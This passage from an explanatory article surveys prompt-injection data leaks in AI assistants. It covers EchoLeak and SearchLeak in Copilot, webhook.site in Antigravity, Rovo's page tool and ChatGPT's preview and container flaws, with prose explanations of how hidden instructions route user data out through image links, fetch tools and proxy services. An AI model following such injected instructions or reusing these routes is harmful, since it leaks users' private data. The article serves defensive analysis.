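Rehberger had reported this gap and several others to OpenAI in October 2024. Before publishing, he asked several times over a month whether OpenAI had fixed them, and got no answer. He noticed that the check was no longer visible in the browser, so OpenAI was changing something. He recommended that the company publish its list of safe domains and let business customers set their own.

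A domain on such a list can also expire, which lets someone else register it. Salesforce, which sells customer-management software, let the page of its Agentforce assistant load images only from listed domains, but one of them had expired. As Willison recounts, researchers at Noma Security registered that domain in 2025 and used it to receive data about a company's sales contacts. Salesforce corrected the list and added a check that keeps the assistant from producing links to untrusted domains.

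Google's programming tool Antigravity had a list of sites its agent's browser could visit. By default, the list included webhook.site, a service that lets anyone create a web address and watch the requests that reach it. In November 2025, the security company PromptArmor showed that instructions in tiny print on a web page could make the agent send a programmer's cloud passwords to such an address.

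The people who compiled these lists probably checked whether each site was reputable. For a data leak, it matters more whether a stranger can read data sent to the site, which is much harder to establish for a large domain with many services and customers.

### Two leaks through Microsoft's own services

Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that can search a company's emails and files, had three defenses against leaks in early 2025. A classifier checked incoming text for prompt injections, a filter removed external links and images from Copilot's answers, and a content security policy limited which domains the browser could load images from. Researchers at Aim Security got past all three with a single email, in an attack they called EchoLeak.

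*EchoLeak* describes how an attack got past the defenses. The classifier missed the instructions because the email seemed to address its human recipient and didn't mention an assistant. The filter recognized the usual markdown notation for links and images but not a less common one that does the same thing. The policy stopped the browser from contacting the attacker's server directly, but it allowed a Microsoft Teams service that fetched other web addresses on request, so the browser sent the stolen data to Teams, which passed it on.

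The victim only had to ask Copilot a later question that made it retrieve the email along with internal documents. They didn't have to open the email or click anything. The email also contained an instruction not to mention the email, so Copilot's answer didn't show where the instructions had come from.

Aim Security reported EchoLeak in January 2025, and Microsoft finished fixing it in May. The fix included removing the less common notation and embedded images from outside material before Copilot reads it. Customers didn't have to install anything, and Microsoft found no sign that anyone had used the attack. EchoLeak received an entry in the public catalog of software flaws, CVE-2025-32711. A year earlier, MITRE had told Schwartzman that it couldn't list a flaw in a web service that customers don't control.

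Rehberger had demonstrated leaks without a click in ChatGPT and Bing Chat two years before, so *EchoLeak* overstates its case when it presents its attack as the first known use of prompt injection to steal data from a real product. The attack is more informative as a test of layered defenses. Each layer had a gap, and one gap per layer was enough for the researchers to get through.

In June 2026, the attack on Copilot's enterprise search that began with a pre-filled link exposed much the same weakness. According to Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026), Microsoft converted Copilot's answers to plain code text to make them harmless, but only after Copilot had finished writing. The browser displayed the answer as it arrived, so it requested the image before the conversion. The policy allowed images from Bing. Bing's image search fetched a picture from whatever address it received, and so delivered the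 data, as Teams had done a year earlier.

Microsoft rated the flaw, CVE-2026-42824, critical and fixed it. Varonis advises companies to clean an assistant's output before the browser displays any of it, and to treat every allowed domain that fetches addresses for others as a possible leak.

This makes the 2023 domain lists look a little less safe than they did then. Bing Chat's list had only four entries, but one was www.bing.com. An attacker could perhaps have used Bing's image search at the time if it already worked the same way.

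### OpenAI's check of the exact address

In January 2026, OpenAI described a rule that checks the exact web address rather than whether its domain is trustworthy. Before ChatGPT automatically opens a page or loads an image, the software looks for the address in an index of public web addresses, which a crawler compiles without access to anyone's conversations. An address in the index exists independently of the chat, so it is unlikely to contain the user's secrets. If the address isn't there, the agent has to try another site, or the user sees a warning that the link may include information from the conversation.

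Suppose a malicious prompt makes ChatGPT write Dana's phone number into an address at example.com. The crawler has almost certainly never encountered that address, so the image doesn't load. The rule would also have stopped Rehberger's attack through windows.net, because an index entry for one address on that domain doesn't approve the others.

OpenAI says only that a public address is much less likely to contain private data. An attacker could still send information through the choice of address, as Rehberger did with his alphabet of images. With a thousand indexed addresses, sending a ten-digit phone number would take at least four requests instead of one.

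According to *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026), OpenAI calls the check Safe Url and also applies it to the pages that users and agents visit in Atlas, its browser, and to searches and page visits by Deep Research, which compiles reports from many sources. Small programs that ChatGPT writes in Canvas, its editing workspace, run in an isolated sandbox that is supposed to ask the user before it contacts anyone unexpectedly.

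Most attacks that OpenAI knows of fail earlier because the model refuses to follow them. But in one test, a malicious email that outside researchers reported in 2025 worked on ChatGPT half the time. In the terms used for Mistral's fix, p, the chance that the model obeys, was 0.5. Once the model obeys, a leak depends on q, the chance that the software lets the data out.

### Images from a summarized page

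Three months after OpenAI described the address check, the security company Permiso found that ChatGPT still loaded images chosen by an attacker. For the tests in Permiso's *ChatGPhish*, published in May 2026, researchers added instructions to a web page and to a project description on GitHub. They opened these pages in Firefox and asked ChatGPT for a summary. ChatGPT summarized the page correctly, then added a fake security alert with a link or an image the researchers had chosen.

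ChatGPT loaded the image without a click, and the researchers' server recorded the user's internet address, browser type and the exact time of the summary. An attacker could use this to confirm that a particular person had read a particular page with ChatGPT's help. No text from the conversation reached the server, because the researchers had written the whole image address into the page beforehand and it was the same for every reader.

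Safe Url checks an address for information the assistant learned in the conversation, and an address written in advance doesn't contain any. It's less clear how the images satisfied the rule that an address must be in the public index, because a crawler seems unlikely to have found pictures made for a test. OpenAI may be more lenient with addresses from a page the user has asked about. Wu and colleagues found in early 2024 that the older check approved any address already in the conversation.

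If so, a page might be able to offer ChatGPT several images and have it pick one based on what the user had said. Permiso didn't test this, so the evidence shows tracking but not theft of chat text.

Permiso was more worried about fraud. The image could be a QR code, which the user scans with a phone, so the computer's usual warnings about suspicious links never appear. OpenAI first replied that it couldn't reproduce the problem. It then marked a more detailed report as "Not Applicable" and later as a duplicate of an earlier one. The last label suggests OpenAI already knew about the behavior, but Permiso hadn't heard of a fix when it published.

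### What Google, Microsoft and Anthropic allow

Google chose a rule close to Mistral's for its Gemini assistant. In October 2025, the software security company Checkmarx told Google and Microsoft about leaks in Gemini and Copilot Chat. Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents* quotes Google as saying that Gemini's software identifies external image addresses and doesn't display them. Checkmarx agreed that this prevents leaks that happen without a click.

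Gemini could still write an ordinary link with private data in its address, and clicking it sent the data to the attacker. Google removes links to sites that its Safe Browsing service lists as malicious, but an attacker can register a new domain that isn't listed yet. Google closed the report after four days, saying a fix wasn't feasible and the problem wasn't severe enough to track as a security flaw.

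Google's point about feasibility is reasonable, because a helpful link may also contain something the user typed, such as their street in a map link. A filter therefore can't remove every link that repeats part of the conversation without removing some helpful ones. A warning before the page opens, like OpenAI's, would be less drastic than removing the link.

The rule for Gemini doesn't cover all Google products. In November 2025, Willison quoted a researcher who had found that Google's Antigravity displayed outside images and could leak data through them. Google had told the researcher that this behavior was intended, but its public list of known issues for Antigravity included data theft by prompt injection, and the company said it was working on fixes.

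Checkmarx researchers showed Copilot Chat requesting an image whose address contained a secret key from a programmer's computer. The instructions to do this could come from an online article that the assistant consulted. Microsoft closed Checkmarx's report without a fix on November 4, 2025, because it didn't consider the behavior a security vulnerability.

Microsoft's reasons were that the attack required the user to do several things that aren't part of the default setup, that it didn't work reliably in different environments, and that the product displayed warnings. Microsoft also assumes that people in such a workplace review and trust the code they choose to run. It passed the report to its engineers so they could look for ways to make the behavior clearer to users.

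A few months earlier, Microsoft (2025) had said that it treats a prompt injection as a vulnerability when it affects the user's security, for example by allowing data theft. It also said that it blocks image leaks deterministically, with a fixed rule that applies whatever the model writes. It had looked for variants of the leak after Rehberger's report on Bing Chat, and it blocked certain untrusted links. For the remaining risks, it relied on the user's consent. For instance, Copilot can draft an email in Outlook, but the user has to send it.

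The extra steps and the warnings are fair reasons to rate the Copilot Chat leak as less serious. The argument about trusted code is weaker, because a programmer who asks an assistant a question hasn't chosen to trust an article that the assistant finds on the web, and may never see it. Checkmarx recommended a strict content security policy for assistants that run in a browser, in addition to filtering the markdown.

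In September 2025, Anthropic introduced a tool that lets Claude fetch web pages. According to its documentation, which Willison quotes, Claude can't open an address it has put together itself, only one that has already appeared in the conversation, for example in the user's message or in search results. Willison tested the Claude app and found the same restriction.

The rule stops the simplest leak, in which the model adds a phone number to the attacker's address. It resembles the older ChatGPT check, which Wu and colleagues defeated by getting private data into text that a plugin returned. Anthropic partly prevents this by excluding addresses that Claude produces by running code on Anthropic's servers. But developers often paste outside text into the user message, and any address in that text then counts as allowed. An attacker could presumably also list several complete addresses and have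 Claude choose one, as Schwartzman did with ChatGPT. Anthropic acknowledges that some risk remains and advises developers not to use the tool where Claude handles both sensitive data and untrusted text. Developers can also limit the tool to a list of domains.

The companies' rules compare as follows:

| Company | Images from other sites | Links and pages | Date of the rule or statement |
|---|---|---|---|
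| Mistral | LeChat doesn't load them | No rule announced with the image fix | September 2024 |
| OpenAI | ChatGPT loads them automatically if the exact address is in a public index | The same check for pages an agent opens, and a warning for unverified links | January and March 2026 |
| Google | Gemini doesn't display them | Gemini removes links to known malicious sites | By October 2025 |
| Microsoft | Fixed rules block known image leaks | Fixed rules block certain untrusted links, and some actions need consent | July 2025 |
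| Anthropic | Claude's web page loads them after a click | Claude opens only addresses already in the conversation | July 2023 and September 2025 |

Some of these rules may have changed since. It's unclear whether LeChat still blocks all external images now that it can search the web.

Mistral's and Google's image rules are the easiest to reason about because they don't require judging which addresses are safe. OpenAI's rule lets users see more of the web, but it depends on what the crawler has found and how consistently the software applies the check. Anthropic's rule for pages needs no index, but it relies on the conversation to determine which addresses are safe, and an attacker's text ends up in that conversation.

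### Rovo's unguarded tool

A rule for images does not restrict a tool that opens web pages. This gap can be large, as it is in Rovo, an assistant from the software company Atlassian. Rovo works with Jira, where teams track tasks, and Confluence, where they keep documents.

In PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls*, from August 2026, a user uploads a guide found online and asks Rovo to organize some Jira tasks. Hidden instructions in the guide make Rovo attach the contents of tasks and documents to the attacker's web address. Rovo then opens the address with its tool for fetching pages. Atlassian had no rule against opening an address the model had just composed, and the tool didn't require the user's approval. A user who reopens the chat later sees ordinary suggestions for their tasks and no sign of the theft.

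Atlassian let companies turn off web search for everyone in the organization, but the attack still worked because the setting removed the search function and left the tool for opening the results. An administrator who turned off web search would reasonably have expected the setting to remove both.

Rovo also displayed markdown images from the model's answers, which PromptArmor listed as a second way to send data out. Copying Mistral's fix would have closed that route but left the page tool open. PromptArmor reported the problems to Atlassian on May 23, 2026. Atlassian thanked the researchers and assigned a case number but didn't answer their later messages. Rovo was still vulnerable when they published more than two months after the report.

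The earlier formula for an image leak, p × q, needs one q for each feature that can make a network request. An attacker who knows the product will choose the feature with the highest value:

chance of a leak = p × max(q_image, q_page tool, q_preview, …)

A hypothetical assistant with p = 0.5 that loads every image and opens every page has a 0.5 × 1 = 50% chance of a leak. If the company blocks all external images, q_image falls to zero, but the chance of a leak is still 50% because the attacker can use the page tool instead. Blocking images lowers the total risk only if the other features have effective rules of their own.

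### What Lockdown Mode turns off

OpenAI's Lockdown Mode applies this reasoning to many features at once. The company introduced it for large organizations in February 2026 and began offering it to personal accounts on June 4. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) describes it as an optional setting for a small number of people with high security needs, such as executives, and says most users don't need it.

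OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, the current help page, lists what changes:

| Feature | In Lockdown Mode |
|---|---|
| Web browsing | Only stored copies of pages, which may be out of date |
| Images in answers | ChatGPT may not show them and doesn't fetch any from the web |
| Deep Research | Off |
| Agent mode, in which ChatGPT carries out tasks on websites | Off |
| Programs written in Canvas | No network access |
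| Downloading files for analysis | Off, but users can upload files themselves |
| Connected apps on personal accounts | No live access or changes that conflict with the protections |
| Memory, file uploads and image generation | Unchanged |
| Codex, OpenAI's programming agent | Network access unchanged |

Stored pages protect users because reading one doesn't send a request to the original site. If a user asks ChatGPT to summarize a stored copy of a malicious page, the model may still follow the instructions on it, but neither the user's browser nor OpenAI should send a request to the attacker's server. OpenAI warns that those instructions can still make the answer wrong.

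The mode takes away most of what ChatGPT gained after 2023. Dana could still get help with a letter she pasted in, and Alice with her job application. But ChatGPT couldn't look up today's news or fill in a website form for them, and it might not show a photograph from a page it had read. Users can switch the mode off for a single chat when it gets in the way. That's convenient, but OpenAI itself objected to strict domain lists because frequent obstacles teach people to click through them.

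In larger organizations, administrators decide which connected apps remain available. OpenAI advises them to avoid apps they don't trust and to be careful with actions that change something in a trusted app. For instance, an assistant that adds a comment to a shared document can leak data without loading an image or opening a web page, because the attacker may be able to read the comment.

### The HTML preview

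Lockdown Mode didn't cover a feature that displays web pages inside ChatGPT. When ChatGPT writes the code for a page, the user can preview the result in the chat. OpenAI ran these previews in a sandbox so that they couldn't read data from the app or contact other sites without the user's consent.

Researchers at the security company Check Point found that pop-up windows could get around this sandbox. ChatGPT blocked direct attempts to open one, but a page could open one indirectly, and the sandbox's restrictions didn't apply to the new window. The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026) reports that an attacker could use this to send chat messages out even with Lockdown Mode on. In the desktop app, the victim didn't have to click anything.

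The attack could start with a malicious custom GPT, a shared chat or a prompt that the victim pasted. The attacker also controlled what appeared in the new window, which could be a fake ChatGPT update containing malware. OpenAI fixed the flaw on September 18, 2026, and Check Point published its findings in early November.

About a week earlier, researchers at Parameter Labs had described a different flaw in the same preview. If someone opened an attacker's shared conversation and clicked the preview once, the attacker could take over their ChatGPT account, because the attacker's code ran as if it were part of ChatGPT's own site.

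Neither flaw shows that Lockdown Mode's other restrictions failed. The image rule would still have stopped a prompt like T10, if such a prompt had worked on ChatGPT. But OpenAI had promised to protect the whole conversation, so it had to find every feature that could make a request, including one that most people would think of as a way to look at their own work.

### A channel between ChatGPT accounts

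ChatGPT can also run code, for example to analyze a spreadsheet, and Check Point found two leaks in that feature in 2026. *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (Check Point Research, March 2026) describes a hidden connection to the public internet from the supposedly isolated environment where the code runs. A single malicious prompt could use it to send out the user's messages and uploaded files.

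The leak that Check Point Research reported on September 8 worked without an internet connection. OpenAI runs each account's code in a separate container, a closed-off environment with its own files. Containers from different accounts couldn't contact each other directly, but they could all reach one internal service. According to TechRadar's *A worrying ChatGPT bug let strangers read Gmail messages*, any container could attach text to an item on that service, and any other container could read it.

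An attacker could use the service to pass data between ChatGPT accounts. The victim's ChatGPT collected data from a connected Gmail account and left it on the service, where the attacker's ChatGPT account retrieved it. *ChatGPT Flaw Could Let Attackers Steal Gmail Data Across User Accounts* (Divya, 2026) reports that the hidden task could arrive in a malicious prompt, a shared conversation or a custom GPT, and that the victim saw a normal answer to their own question.

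No check of web addresses could have caught this attack, because the data never went to an outside address. Lockdown Mode's stored pages are meant to keep live requests from leaving OpenAI's network, and this attack sent none out. The mode would probably have helped owners of personal accounts, since it limits live access to services such as Gmail, but text already in the chat might have remained exposed. OpenAI had patched the flaw by the time Divya reported on it on September 9.
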